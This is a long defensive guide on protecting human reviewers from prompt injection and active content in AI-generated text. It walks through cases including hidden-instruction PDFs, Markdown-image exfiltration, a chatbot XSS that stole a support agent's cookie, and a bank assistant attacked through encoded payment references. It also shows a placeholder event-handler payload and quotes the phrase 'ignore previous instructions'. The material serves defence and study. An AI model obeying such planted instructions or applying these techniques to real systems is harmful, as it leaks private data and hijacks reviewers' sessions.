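# Protecting human reviewers from instructions and active content in AI-generated text

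## How text from a language model can act on the person reading it

A large language model is a program that produces text by repeatedly predicting the next small piece. People read that text in chat windows, log viewers, customer-support consoles, programmers' terminals and approval screens, where a person allows or refuses an action that an AI agent proposes. Model output means any text a language model produces, including text it copies from a source. A reviewer is a person who reads model output to check, approve, label or investigate it, and a review tool is the software they use to read it.

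Model output can contain code, images, links or hidden characters that trigger actions in the review tool, as well as sentences that get the reviewer to act. An outsider who can get the model to read an email, web page or document can choose part of what appears on the reviewer's screen, so this content often doesn't come from the user or the company behind the model.

### From a document to a reviewer's screen

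Suppose a supplier sends a company a proposal as a PDF. On the last page, in white text on a white background, the supplier has typed a request that any AI system summarising the document end with the words "blue teapot". When an employee asks the company's assistant for a summary, the assistant's software combines the employee's request and all the text of the PDF, including the white text, into one input for the model. The model returns four sound paragraphs followed by "blue teapot", and the software saves the summary in a log. A reviewer who later samples the log for quality sees the two words in the company's own viewer, in the same typeface and under the same logo as the rest of the summary, with nothing to show that a supplier chose them.

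This is indirect prompt injection, which means planting instructions in material a model will read so that the model follows the attacker instead of its user. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced the term in *Not what you've signed up for*. The attack is "indirect" because the attacker never types anything into the target system. Microsoft (2025) describes the same sequence with a web page in place of the PDF, and adds that the attacker needs no special file format and can use a plain text file.

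*On Violations of LLM Review Policies* (Agarwal, Dudik and colleagues, 2026) describes how the organisers of ICML, a machine-learning conference, hid an instruction in the PDF of every submitted paper. It asked any language model to include two particular phrases in its review, and the organisers drew a new pair for each paper from a list of 170,000. In tests shortly before the submission deadline, most leading models had complied more than 80% of the time. The organisers wanted to catch referees who had agreed to write without a model, and they caught 795 reviews, about 1% of the total. Each of those reviews was submitted by a referee who had left the phrases in. The count doesn't show how often people miss planted text, because referees who spotted the phrases could delete them and go uncounted. NDTV reported a similar case in which Cameron Mattis, an executive at the payments company Stripe,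 put a line in a LinkedIn profile asking language models for a flan recipe, and received a recruiter's message that included one.

Models follow injected instructions because they have no separate channel for legitimate ones. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C explains that a model's whole input is one run of text, and the model only ever predicts the next token, a word or piece of a word. Developers can make a successful injection less likely by marking off outside text or training the model to give the user's instructions priority. David C doubts that any such measure will eliminate the problem, and advises designers to limit the damage instead. If a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, a language model may be unsuitable for it.

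### What the software does and what the person does

Active content is output that makes the software displaying it do something, such as run a script or contact a server. If an AI-generated summary ended with a script, a poorly secured viewing program might run it with the reviewer's access. If the summary ended with an image, the program might contact the image's server as soon as it displayed the page. The summary could instead end with a message to the reviewer, such as a false warning that their account is locked, with a telephone number to call. The program would then only display words, and any harm would depend on what the reviewer did next.

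Microsoft distinguishes deterministic defences, which guarantee that a particular attack fails even if the system contains a model that behaves unpredictably, from probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed. A designer can rule out active content with deterministic defences, but has only probabilistic defences against a message addressed to the reader.

Display software follows fixed rules, so a review tool can guarantee protection against specific attacks on it. For example, a web browser treats a less-than sign as the possible start of a command in HTML, the language of web pages. If the tool replaces each less-than sign with the code for displaying one, the browser shows the sign instead of treating it as the possible start of a command. This works however the planted text is worded, and even if the injection fooled the model, because the replacement happens after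 the model has finished. But the guarantee covers only the attack the designer thought of, only in displays where the replacement was added, and only until a later change to the tool removes it.

Escaping the less-than sign can stop a browser from treating text as an HTML tag, but English has no character that marks a sentence as an instruction and could be escaped in the same way. "Call this number today" is an attack in one summary and an accurate report of a bank's letter in another, and a filter that removed every sentence that could influence a reader would leave nothing to review. David C similarly argues that blocking the phrase "ignore previous instructions" doesn't protect models, because an attacker can reword the request endlessly. Requests to people can also be reworded endlessly. A tool can frame and label model output so that fewer readers mistake it for a message from the tool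 itself, but some still will.

Software security catalogues show the same split. In *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026) matched ten common risks of language-model applications to CWE, a public list of recurring software weaknesses. Unsafe handling of output matched known entries, including failure to encode output properly. They found no direct equivalent for content that deceives people, which they attributed to the way models generate text, whereas CWE entries describe faults in code. Defending against deception is not hopeless, but developers have no standard code fix to copy.

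Some attacks depend on both the software and the reader. An attack that uses a link, for example, works only if the tool makes the address clickable and the reader clicks it. Showing the address as plain text prevents the click, though a determined reader can still type the address into a browser.

### Inert data, and inert to what

Inert data is output that a tool displays without any software interpreting any part of it as an instruction. Most review tools should aim for this. But text is inert only relative to a particular interpreter, meaning whatever turns the characters into behaviour, and several interpreters may process the same log entry in a week.

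Replacing every less-than sign in the supplier's summary makes it inert in the browser, but it can still cause problems in other programs. An engineer might print the same entry in a terminal, the text window in which programmers type commands. Terminals act on control sequences that begin with an invisible "escape" character, which the browser fix leaves in place. According to MITRE, which maintains CWE, such sequences can move the cursor, clear the screen and fake a prompt, and on some terminals they can run code. *Terminal DiLLMa*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, reports that many language models can emit the escape character. If a manager exports the log to a spreadsheet, a cell that begins with an equals sign may turn into a formula.

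The company might also have a second model grade the summaries. That model could treat any sentence in them as an instruction, even if a tool has carefully encoded the text for the browser. Greshake and colleagues used a mock email assistant to demonstrate how such instructions can spread. The assistant read a planted message, looked up the user's address book and sent the message to the contacts, whose own models could then read it. The reviewer is the last to interpret the text, and no encoding that leaves it legible can prevent it from affecting them.

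A developer's claim that some output is "safe" is incomplete unless it says where the output is safe, such as in the browser. Without that detail, a colleague can't check the claim.

### How the problem got its names

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022. At first, researchers mostly assumed that the attacker was the person typing. In early 2023, Greshake and colleagues instead tested text planted in web pages on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search chatbot, which could read whatever page a user had open in the Edge browser. They steered the chatbot with instructions in HTML comments, which a browser does not show. Its filters missed requests on the page that they normally caught when a user typed them, and in most cases the effect lasted for the rest of the conversation. In one test, Bing Chat told the user that they had won a gift card and should verify an account to claim it. The researchers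 had instructed it to be persuasive without specifying how, and it added the "limited time" pressure unprompted. These demonstrations covered one early product and did not include success rates, so they show that the attack was possible but not how often it would have worked.

Attacks using active content followed within weeks. Many chat interfaces accept Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and images, and convert it to HTML. Willison's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (April 2023) reported Roman Samoilenko's finding that ChatGPT would display a Markdown image whose address carried chat data to an outside server. *EchoLeak* (2025) reports that in January 2025 the security group Aim Labs found a similar flaw in a Microsoft product, which an attacker could exploit by email without the user clicking anything. By mid-2026 Willison had filed 45 posts under the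 tag "exfiltration-attacks", meaning attacks that send private data to someone who should not have it.

OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is a non-profit organisation that publishes ranked lists of software risks. Its first list for language-model applications, the 2023–24 edition, ranked Insecure Output Handling (*LLM02*) second out of ten. The 2025 edition ranked it fifth and renamed it *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*. The definition is almost unchanged and covers insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of model output before it passes to other components. The number of countermeasures grew from three to seven. One of the additions is to choose the encoding according to where the output will go, because more than one interpreter may process it.

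OWASP's core advice has consistently been to "treat the model as any other user", because anyone who can influence the prompt can influence the output. A system that trusts the output therefore gives that person indirect access to whatever the system can reach. This advice applies to model responses passed to back-end functions, but OWASP separately advises developers to encode model output before returning it to users. Together, these recommendations imply that a review tool should treat a summary from the company's own model like a comment from an anonymous visitor to the company's website.

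OWASP (2026) released the next edition in August 2026, and output handling dropped to tenth. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's summary, attributes the drop to other risks becoming more urgent and notes that the entry expanded to cover terminals and displays that automatically fetch outside resources. The ranking gives three-quarters of the weight to a vote among practitioners and one-quarter to 7,714 recorded incidents. Prompt injection came first in the vote, but Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that it would have missed the top ten on incidents alone. OWASP attributes the gap to the effort that teams spend on defence. That may be right, but the counts cannot confirm it, because rare or unrecorded attacks would produce the same low number. A rank across all language-model applications is also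 a poor guide for someone whose whole product is a display. The edition's design advice is more useful to that person. OWASP tells developers to "Stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled" and to build the surrounding system so that nothing important breaks when the model fails.

### Whether the model creates the flaw

That advice assumes that the problem can be fixed in the surrounding system. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, August 2026) defends this assumption. A web application contains components that act on whatever text they receive: a database runs queries, a command tool runs commands, and a browser page runs scripts. Long before language models, these components were dangerous if they trusted text from a stranger. A model placed in front of them turns the stranger's ordinary language into a query, a command or part of a page, and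 the component accepts the result because it came from the model. On this account, the model usually gives the attacker a way to reach an existing flaw rather than creating a new one.

The paper covers eight types of attack, five with documented cases and three that the two researchers constructed by analogy. Scripts in displayed output (cross-site scripting, or XSS) cause harm only when the application treats the model's text as page code. If the application stores the text as a ticket, a report or a chat history, the script may run later, when a different person opens the record. That person may be a reviewer, since most of a reviewer's job is opening other people's records.

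In April 2026, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also tested a concert-ticket assistant with a tool that would fetch any web address, including private administrative pages on its own server. They ran each attack ten times on each of seven models. Llama 3.3 70B complied in all 40 trials in which the attacker typed the request directly, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 never did. The researchers then added an allowlist to the model's instructions: a list of permitted addresses, with all others to be refused. This stopped every direct attempt on every model. But when they planted a customer review claiming that the list now included an administrative page, Llama fetched the page in all ten trials, up from six without the list.

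The experiment supports only part of the paper's general claim. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built the flaw into the assistant on purpose, so the results cannot show where such flaws come from. The evidence for that is the documented cases. The ten trials were not independent because they shared one conversation, and they tested requests from a server, with no display involved. The experiment does show that the same flaw can be harmless with one model and exploitable with another, and that a rule in the prompt is an unreliable way to enforce an allowlist. The researchers conclude that checks in the application's own code matter most because they do not depend on the model's compliance. This is good news for a review tool's owner, who controls the code but usually not the model.

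The argument does not apply to messages addressed to the reader. A false warning can work without exploiting an older software flaw, and the model may write the persuasive part itself, as Bing Chat did with the gift card.

A language model can give new people access to a flaw that active content exploits, so it is only limited reassurance that the model did not create the flaw. One of the paper's documented cases involves a type of command tool that often runs on a developer's own machine, where outsiders cannot connect to it. An attacker can still get a command to the tool by planting it in a file that the developer's coding assistant reads. Similarly, an internal log viewer may have displayed text unsafely for years without harm because only colleagues' text reached it. Once the viewer shows summaries of suppliers' PDFs, text from suppliers can reach it as well.

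## Listing every place where model output is shown

The first task is to list every display that model output can reach. The list has to go well beyond the product's own chat window, because applications often save their answers and later show them to support staff and developers or pass them to other programs. The owner of an internal log viewer, for example, can't fix it until someone notices that suppliers' text now reaches it.

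### Following each copy to a screen

The team starts at the point in the code where the application receives the model's answer and lists everywhere the code sends or saves that text, such as the user's screen, a database, a logging service or an email. The team then lists every program that reads from each of those places, and continues until it has followed every copy to a screen or to its deletion. Saved copies need the most care because a new report or dashboard can start reading an old database at any time.

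Some copies of model output are easy to miss. LangSmith, a service that logs what language-model applications do, has a setting that keeps answers out of the log. OSV's *CVE-2026-41182*, an entry in a public database of software flaws, describes how the setting failed for streamed answers, which arrive in small pieces. The software saved each piece as a separate event, and the setting did not apply to events, so the full answer stayed in the log. LangSmith has since fixed the flaw, but before the fix, a team that trusted the setting would have left the log off its list.

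A team can check its list by putting an unusual phrase, such as "blue teapot", in a test document, getting the model to repeat it, and searching every system it can for the phrase a week later. The search will turn up copies that nobody remembered. Someone has to check the remaining systems, such as an outside company's dashboard, by hand. Someone also has to ask engineers and managers what they do with saved answers, because the product's code won't show that answers are being read in an engineer's terminal or a manager's spreadsheet.

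One product can include several displays with different protections. In December 2023 OpenAI added a check on image addresses to ChatGPT, but Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* reports that the macOS and iOS apps lacked it. The post warns that some of a company's own developers may not know about such a protection. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-14898* describes a similar gap in OpenAI's coding assistant, Codex, whose macOS app automatically loaded outside images from model responses. Rapid7 knows of no real attack that used it. Pages for sharing conversations are also displays, and Goyal's *Do the Math* (2026) showed that opening a shared ChatGPT conversation could run an attacker's code in the reader's signed-in session. OpenAI fixed that flaw on October 26, 2026. The inventory therefore needs separate rows for the website, each app and the sharing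 page.

Notifications can cause harm before anyone reads them. Slack and Discord fetch posted links to show a title and a picture. If an attacker gets a chatbot to post a link with private data in its address, the attacker can receive that data when the chat service fetches the link (Willison, 2024).

Email to the user's own inbox can also leak data. According to Microsoft's documentation, Copilot Cowork, an AI agent for office work, asks permission before it sends an email or posts in the chat program Teams. But *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, by the security company PromptArmor, reports that the agent sent messages to its own user without asking. Willison (2026) pointed out that the danger came from how those messages were displayed, since they could load images from an attacker's server.

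The list should also include any model that reads the output, because it may copy what it reads into a verdict or explanation that a person may then read. For example, OpenAI's *Changelog* (2026) records a setting, introduced in October 2026, that has a model approve or refuse some of an agent's requests. The team should trace the reviewing model's text in the same way as the original model's.

### What to record about each display

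The team records who reads each display, what that person can access, what the software interprets, and which outside servers the display can contact. A job title is enough to identify the reader. The access entry should cover everything the reader can see or change while signed in to the tool. An entry that says only "Markdown" for what the software interprets is too vague, because some Markdown viewers load images and others show only headings and bold text. A browser will usually contact any server that a page names unless something restricts it, so the server entry should be "any" if nobody knows which servers a display can contact.

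The reader's access affects how much harm a script can do, but not how much data an image can leak. A script runs with the reader's access, so it can do more harm in an administrator's browser than in a customer's. It may not need an outside server, because it can change records in the tool itself. An image leaks private data that the model has already read and written into the image's address. The same data therefore leaks whoever opens the page, and it can include data that the reader has no permission to see.

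### A leak from an answer that the application had blocked

Companies that build on OpenAI's models can read their applications' past conversations in a log viewer on OpenAI's website. In January 2026, PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* described an attack that used this viewer. PromptArmor built a mock application of the kind that banks use to verify customers' identities, and the attack ran as follows:

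1. The application gave the model a customer's private details, along with text from the web in which an outsider had planted instructions.
2. A user asked the assistant one of its suggested questions about the customer.
3. The model followed the planted instructions and wrote a Markdown image. The image's address pointed to the outsider's server and included the customer's details.
4. A second model, which checked answers before the application displayed them, flagged this one and blocked it. At this point, nothing had leaked.
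5. A developer opened the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer to investigate the flag.
6. The viewer rendered the answer, meaning that it turned the stored characters into a displayed page. To show the image, the developer's browser requested it from the outsider's server, and the request carried the customer's details.

The check in step 4 worked, but it controlled only the application's own screen. PromptArmor lists three other defences with the same limit. An application can show answers as plain text, use a sanitiser to remove disallowed elements from markup, or set a Content Security Policy, which tells the browser which servers and scripts a website's pages may use. A company can add all of these to its own product, but not to a log viewer that OpenAI runs.

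PromptArmor found that several tools for previewing an assistant during development, including OpenAI's Agent Builder, loaded images in the same way. It found the same flaw in a starter application that OpenAI gave developers, so a developer could have unknowingly copied the flaw into a new product.

PromptArmor sells security services, and it built both the application and the attack. Its report shows that the leak was possible but does not describe a real theft. In the Hacker News discussion that takira opened as *OpenAI API Logs*, one commenter called the case narrow, because it needs an application with private data, a blocked answer and someone who later opens the log, and put most of the responsibility on companies that send private data to OpenAI. But an identity-checking tool cannot work without private data, and developers have good reason to investigate blocked answers. In the same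 discussion, Willison argued that the viewer should not load such images. He compared the flaw to stored cross-site scripting, though here the attacker could not run a script.

It is unclear whether OpenAI finished fixing the viewer. Bugcrowd, the company that screens bug reports for OpenAI, closed PromptArmor's report in December 2025 as not applicable, without OpenAI seeing it. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, and on January 22, 2026 it indicated that a fix was under way. PromptArmor's page gives no later news, and OpenAI's changelog lists no repair to the log viewer from then through November 5. But the changelog mostly announces features, so OpenAI may have repaired the viewer without saying so. In June, OpenAI announced that it would retire Agent Builder, one of the affected preview tools. Teams that still use the log viewer should test it before they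 open a flagged answer there.

### How flagging can raise the risk

Flagging an answer sends it to a person who often has more access than the user who asked the question. A customer can usually see one account, while the analyst reviewing flagged answers may be able to open every conversation and change settings. If the review software runs scripts contained in an answer, a planted script gains the analyst's access. A deceptive message is also more useful to an attacker if its reader is an administrator.

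Flagging also concentrates attacks in one place. Suppose one answer in 10,000 contains a planted image, and a detector flags 90% of those answers and 1% of harmless ones. Out of a million answers, it flags 90 of the 100 attacks and 9,999 harmless answers, so about one flagged answer in 112 is an attack. A reviewer who opens a flagged answer is roughly 90 times as likely to encounter an attack as someone who opens an answer at random. A detector with fewer false alarms would concentrate the attacks further.

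Users flag answers too. PromptArmor shows a reply from Perplexity, an AI search service, after the software had removed an image from it. The reply was oddly empty, so a user might reasonably click "thumbs down". A developer investigating the complaint could then open the original answer in a log, with the image still in it. PromptArmor gives no example of a real complaint leading to a leak this way, but the sequence is plausible.

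Teams should still flag suspicious answers, but the queue where reviewers read them needs the strictest display rules in the company. Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) recommends limiting who can open logs and reading flagged conversations in an environment that cannot make outside requests. If the detector is a model that explains its decisions, the same rules should apply to its explanations, because they may quote the planted text.

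### A customer's chat that ran code in a support agent's browser

An attacker may not need to trigger a flag to reach a member of staff. Many support chatbots hand the conversation to a person when the customer asks, and that person then opens the chat history. Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes such a case involving Lena, the customer-support chatbot on computer maker Lenovo's website, which ran on OpenAI's GPT-4.

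Cybernews researchers found that a single message could make Lenovo's chatbot, Lena, answer in HTML that included a command for the browser. Lenovo's server saved the answer in the chat history. If the customer then asked for a human agent, the agent's browser loaded the history and ran the command, which sent the agent's session cookie to an outside server. A session cookie shows a website that the browser has already signed in, so an attacker who had the agent's cookie could enter the support system without a username or password and potentially read other customers' chats.

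The attacker in this case was the customer, who typed the request directly without needing to plant a document. The command also ran in the customer's own browser, where an attacker would have stolen only their own cookie. A security test of only the customer's chat window could have found the flaw and rated it as minor. An inventory's row for the support console would have shown that its readers could open many customers' chats and that it ran scripts.

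Lenovo confirmed the cross-site scripting flaw and said it had protected its customers. ITPro's *Flaw in Lenovo’s customer service AI chatbot* reports that the researchers told Lenovo on July 22, 2025, and that Lenovo acknowledged the report on August 6 and mitigated the flaw by August 18. Cybernews suggested that an attacker might also be able to run commands on Lenovo's computers, but its researchers did not try this. According to CPO Magazine's *Researchers Able to Abuse Lenovo’s “People-Pleasing” AI Chatbot*, it is unclear whether anyone exploited the flaw before Cybernews reported it.

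### Why defences inside an agent do not protect the screen

Some designs try to limit what planted instructions can do inside the agent itself. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed dividing an assistant's work between two models. The privileged model takes the user's requests and can use tools, for example to send email. The quarantined model reads outside text and has no tools. Ordinary software called the Controller passes work between them. It gives the privileged model only the names of stored texts, such as VAR1, not their contents.

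Suppose a user asks for a summary of their latest email:

1. The privileged model tells the Controller to fetch the email, and the Controller stores it as VAR1.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of VAR1.
3. The Controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the resulting summary as VAR2.
4. The privileged model tells the Controller to display VAR2 to the user.

Instructions planted in the email may take over the quarantined model, but that model cannot send or delete anything. The privileged model can, but it never reads the email or the summary. Willison allows one exception, when the quarantined model's task is to choose from a fixed set of categories. The Controller can then check that the answer is one of them and pass it to the privileged model.

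The user still reads VAR2 in full. If the sender hid a request for the words "blue teapot" in the email, those words can appear in the summary, and so can a link or an image. Willison wrote that a model that may mix untrusted text with private data should not be able to produce outside links or images. The Controller or the display has to enforce that rule, because the quarantined model may be following an attacker's instructions. Willison, who called the overall solution "pretty bad", also warned that a summary could persuade the user to paste private data into an attacker's website.

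In 2025, researchers at Google DeepMind published CaMeL, a system that addresses a flaw in the dual-model design. Willison explains that CaMeL turns the user's request into a small program and checks at each step that data goes only to the right places. When a user asks for a summary, the user's screen is presumably one of those places. The agent's design does not control how the display then handles the text, so an agent with strong internal defences needs the same rows in the inventory as any other.

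### An example inventory with six displays

For example, an online marketplace might have a support assistant that answers customers' questions by reading product descriptions written by outside sellers. Any seller could then plant text that the model will read. The customer sees the answer in a chat window, and the application saves a copy. If the customer asks for a person, a support agent opens the saved chat in a console. A checking model sends suspicious answers to a queue for the safety team. The application also posts answers about delivery problems in the couriers' chat channel, exports each week's answers to a manager's spreadsheet, and writes every answer to a log file that engineers read in a terminal.

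The team rates each reader's access as low if the reader can see only their own orders or a day's delivery addresses, medium if they can see every customer's records, and high if they can change accounts or systems. The team also rates each display's capabilities as low if the display only shows text, medium if it can contact an outside server or alter what is on the screen, and high if it runs scripts.

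| Rank | Display | Reader and access | What the software interprets | Outside servers it can contact |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Support console | Support agents, who can change any account and issue refunds (high) | HTML, including scripts (high) | Any |
| 2 | Log file in a terminal | Engineers, who can change the live system (high) | Control sequences that can hide or rewrite lines (medium) | None found so far |
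| 3 | Flagged-answer queue | Safety team, who can read every conversation and customer record (medium) | Markdown, including images (medium) | Any |
| 4 | Weekly spreadsheet | A manager, who can read every customer's records (medium) | Formulas (medium) | Depends on the program's settings |
| 5 | Courier alerts | Couriers, who can see the day's delivery addresses (low) | Links, which the chat service fetches for previews (medium) | Any, through the chat service |
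| 6 | Customer chat window | One customer, who can see their own orders (low) | Nothing, because it shows plain text (low) | The marketplace's own server |

The team doesn't need a formula for this ranking, because each display rates at least as high as the one below it on both measures. The queue and the spreadsheet tie, but the team ranks the queue higher because the checking model concentrates attacks there. If one display had a more powerful reader and another had more capable software, the team would have to judge which was worse. The team would also move the terminal up if it found engineers using one that could run code from a control sequence.

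The team doesn't have to make repairs in ranked order. The courier alerts rank fifth, but if the couriers use Slack, the application can turn off link previews with two settings, so the team could fix that row the same day. The team could also remove the model's answer from the alerts and send couriers only an order number, which would take the alerts off the list.

The team should date the inventory and trace the copies again whenever anyone, including a supplier, adds a display. In June 2026, for example, OpenAI released a dashboard that shows blocked requests to its customers. If the marketplace used that dashboard, the team would have to find out whether it displays any of the blocked text and, if so, add a seventh row.

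## Showing model output as text, not code

The support console ranks first on the marketplace's list because it renders saved chats as HTML, so a seller can plant text that runs as a script in a support agent's browser. The console's owner can remove that risk by showing the chats as plain text. Deciding how much formatting reviewers need is harder, because every kind of formatting gives the browser something to interpret.

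### How a browser tells text from markup

A browser reads HTML with a program called a parser, which treats characters as text until it meets one that may begin markup. A less-than sign followed by a letter opens a tag, such as `<b>`, which makes the words after it bold. A tag can have attributes, which are settings with a name and a value. Some attributes, called event handlers, contain a command the browser runs when something happens, such as a click or an image failing to load. An ampersand can begin a character code, such as `&lt;`, which the browser displays as a less-than sign without opening a tag.

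If a page inserts a model's answer as HTML, the browser builds elements from any tags in the answer. The browser's parser has no information about who wrote the tags, so any event handlers in them get the same powers as the website's own code. A planted handler can then read the page and send requests to the website as the signed-in reader.

Whether a page treats a model's answer as text or markup often depends on one property name in its code. The browser displays anything assigned to `textContent` as plain text, but parses anything assigned to `innerHTML` as HTML. React, a popular library for building web pages, shows text by default and requires developers to use `dangerouslySetInnerHTML` to insert HTML. An auditor can search a review tool's code for these names.

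Browsers don't run a `<script>` element that a page inserts through `innerHTML`, but they do run event handlers inserted the same way. A tester who tries only a script element could wrongly conclude that the page is safe.

Output encoding means replacing characters that have special meaning to a program with forms it displays literally. For HTML, those characters are the ampersand, angle brackets, and straight single and double quotation marks.

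### Output shown at once and output stored for someone else

When a page displays a reply as soon as it arrives, a script in the reply runs in the browser of the person who asked. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a prompt that instructed the Chinese chatbot DeepSeek to decode a script and reply with only the decoded text. The script was written in Base64, a notation that represents any data with letters, digits and a few symbols. DeepSeek's chat page inserted the reply as HTML, and the script ran. To harm someone else this way, an attacker has to get that person to paste the prompt, or plant it in something the model will read.

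If the application saves the reply, the script can also reach a later reader, as it did at Lenovo. Quarkslab, a security company, used this to take over an administrator's account on a client's live system, then published a demonstration of the attack using a mock medical assistant. The testers got the model to put a script in their own conversation. Each conversation had a predictable web address, and the server never checked whether the person opening it was the owner. If an administrator followed a link to the conversation, the script ran and sent the administrator's session cookie to the testers. Quarkslab mainly recommended validating and encoding every response from the model.

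The client could also have set the cookie so that scripts couldn't read it. That would have stopped this theft, but a script running in the administrator's page doesn't need to read the cookie, because the browser attaches it to any request the script makes to the same website.

### A payment reference that ran code in a bank customer's session

Positive Security's *Banking AI XSS* (2026) describes how an outsider could run a script in a bank customer's session by sending the customer an invoice or a few cents. The security company tested the AI assistant of its own unnamed business bank. The assistant could look up transactions and add payees, and the bank's page inserted its replies as HTML. A researcher asked it to add a payee whose name contained an image tag, and a broken image appeared in the reply. A filter blocked a well-known event handler but missed a more obscure one, and the researcher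 had a script running within two minutes.

So far the researcher could attack only their own session, so the company looked for ways to get the text in from outside. It first tried a PDF with white text on a white background, which the customer would upload before asking the assistant to add the payee named in the file. The hidden text was a request to repeat the payee's full name, on the grounds that the name was strange and needed checking. This mild request worked, while a blunt order addressed to the AI was more likely to trigger the bank's safeguards.

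The other route was the payment reference, the short message that accompanies a bank transfer. SEPA, the euro payment system, limits references to 140 characters from a restricted set that excludes angle brackets, so a reference could hardly open a tag on an ordinary web page. The researchers replaced each forbidden character with an abbreviation in round brackets, split the text across two one-cent transfers, and added an instruction to join the parts and decode them. The assistant's reply then contained a complete tag, which neither transfer had.

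The character limits filtered the input as intended, but the model processed the text afterwards. Any filter on a model's input has this weakness, because the model can decode, translate or assemble text that looked harmless. The application therefore has to encode the model's output.

In the demonstration, the script used the customer's session to fetch their email address from the bank and send it to an outside server. The bank had no Content Security Policy to stop this. Only the bank's multi-factor authentication, which requires a second proof of identity, still prevented the script from emptying the account.

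Positive Security reported the flaw on July 13, 2026. The bank at first said customers could use it only against themselves, but two days later said that it should be fixed. In a quick retest, the assistant's replies always seemed to be encoded. Before the fix, only some had been encoded, apparently because the model sometimes encoded the characters itself. A tool's owner who sees encoded output in one test should check that the application's code encoded it.

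The bank's system automatically forwarded one of the researchers' conversations to a human agent, but they did not find out whether the agent's screen would have run the script. They also did not test the AI agents that the bank advertises for analysing transactions. Their evidence for the payment route is weaker than for the PDF. They wanted to avoid sending many strange transfers through live banking systems, so in their video the customer's own prompt repeats some of the planted instructions. They claim in their summary that a request to list the month's transactions could trigger the attack, but the video does not show an ordinary request triggering it without those repeated instructions.

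### One answer on five displays

Suppose a seller on the marketplace plants the following text in a product description, and the support assistant repeats it in an answer:

`**Paid** <b onclick="SCRIPT">today</b>`

The asterisks are Markdown for bold. `SCRIPT` stands for an attacker's command, which the browser would run when someone clicked "today". The support agent would see one of these results:

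| How the console displays the answer | What appears on screen |
|---|---|
| HTML with no protection | `**Paid**` **today** (a click runs the command) |
| Plain text | `**Paid** <b onclick="SCRIPT">today</b>` |
| Encoded text with a few fixed styles | **Paid** `<b onclick="SCRIPT">today</b>` |
| Markdown with raw HTML disabled | **Paid** `<b onclick="SCRIPT">today</b>`, or **Paid** today |
| Sanitised HTML | `**Paid**` **today** (a click does nothing) |

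The unprotected display and the sanitised one look the same until someone clicks, so a team can't judge a display by its appearance. The four protected displays are in order from safest to riskiest.

### Plain text and fixed styles

Plain text shows the reviewer the visible characters that the model produced, including any planted tag, so it is the best choice for flagged answers and security investigations, where the tag is the evidence. But it is tiring to read, because long answers fill with asterisks and hash signs, and browsers run lines together unless the developer tells them to keep the line breaks. The main danger is that someone later switches the display to HTML to make it look better. In the example, the agent would then notice that the tag had disappeared and "today" had turned bold.

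When a log viewer serves saved answers as separate files, the server has to label each file as plain text. A browser parses a file as HTML if it is labelled that way, even if the developer meant it to be a text log. The server also needs a setting that stops the browser from guessing a different type.

A tool can make text easier to read by encoding the whole answer and then adding a few styles of its own, such as bold, headings and a fixed-width font for code. The reviewer still sees any planted tags as text. These fixed styles are safe because the developer wrote every character of their tags in advance. If the tool adds its styles before encoding, its own tags also appear on screen as text, which is ugly but harmless. Letting the answer supply part of a tag is dangerous. For example, if the tool coloured a label with whatever colour name the model gave, an unencoded quotation mark could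 end the colour setting and let the text after it add an event handler.

### Markdown with raw HTML disabled

A Markdown parser formats lists, tables, quotations and links for the reviewer, so the developer doesn't have to write each style. But Markdown's original design lets an author mix in HTML, and a parser that follows it passes planted tags to the page. Many parsers can disable raw HTML, and some do so by default. Depending on the parser, the tag in the example then appears as text or disappears. Showing it as text is better for a review tool, because the agent learns that someone planted it.

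If both "Paid" and "today" are bold, raw HTML is on. An add-on for formulas or diagrams may need raw HTML and switch it back on long after a team has checked the setting.

Disabling raw HTML does not make links safe. If a link's address begins with `javascript:`, the browser can run the rest as code when someone clicks it. Good parsers block such addresses. A developer who writes a separate check should run it on the finished link, because Markdown parsers decode character codes in addresses, and a search of the original text for `javascript:` would miss an address that used a code for the colon. Ordinary links and images can leak data without any script, so they need separate controls.

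### Sanitised HTML

Some reviewers need to see HTML rendered, for example when checking a marketing email that a model wrote. A sanitiser gives them the most formatting, but it can hide an attack. In the example, it removes the event handler and leaves a bold word, with no sign that anything was removed. A review tool that sanitises should therefore also offer the original as plain text.

Sanitising HTML can fail because the browser may parse the markup differently from the sanitiser. DOMPurify, a widely used sanitiser, parses the HTML, cleans it and returns it as a string. The page usually assigns that string to `innerHTML` (Braun, *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()*), so the browser parses it again. *Two Bypasses for Chrome's Sanitizer API* (Searchlight Cyber, 2026) explains that HTML's rules are complicated enough for the second parse to differ from the first and produce a live tag.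 Attackers have used such differences repeatedly. Searchlight Cyber considers DOMPurify safe for now but sees no theoretical obstacle to another bypass.

Several DOMPurify flaws published in 2026 depended on how developers had configured it or where they put the cleaned result:

- Some HTML elements, such as `noscript`, make the browser read their contents by different rules. GitLab's *CVE-2026-0540* (2026) describes how text inside an attribute could become a live tag when a page placed the cleaned HTML inside one of them. The flaw affected versions 3.1.3 to 3.3.1, and some older ones.
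- INCIBE's *CVE-2026-65912* (2026) reports that `javascript:` links could survive in versions before 3.3.2 if a developer had supplied a custom rule for accepting attributes.
- Some page-building frameworks, such as Vue 2, run expressions that they find between double braces. According to Lutra Security's *DOMPurify has a SAFE_FOR_TEMPLATES bypass in RETURN_DOM mode* (2026), a setting meant to remove these expressions failed when DOMPurify returned finished page elements instead of a string. Version 3.4.0 fixed this.

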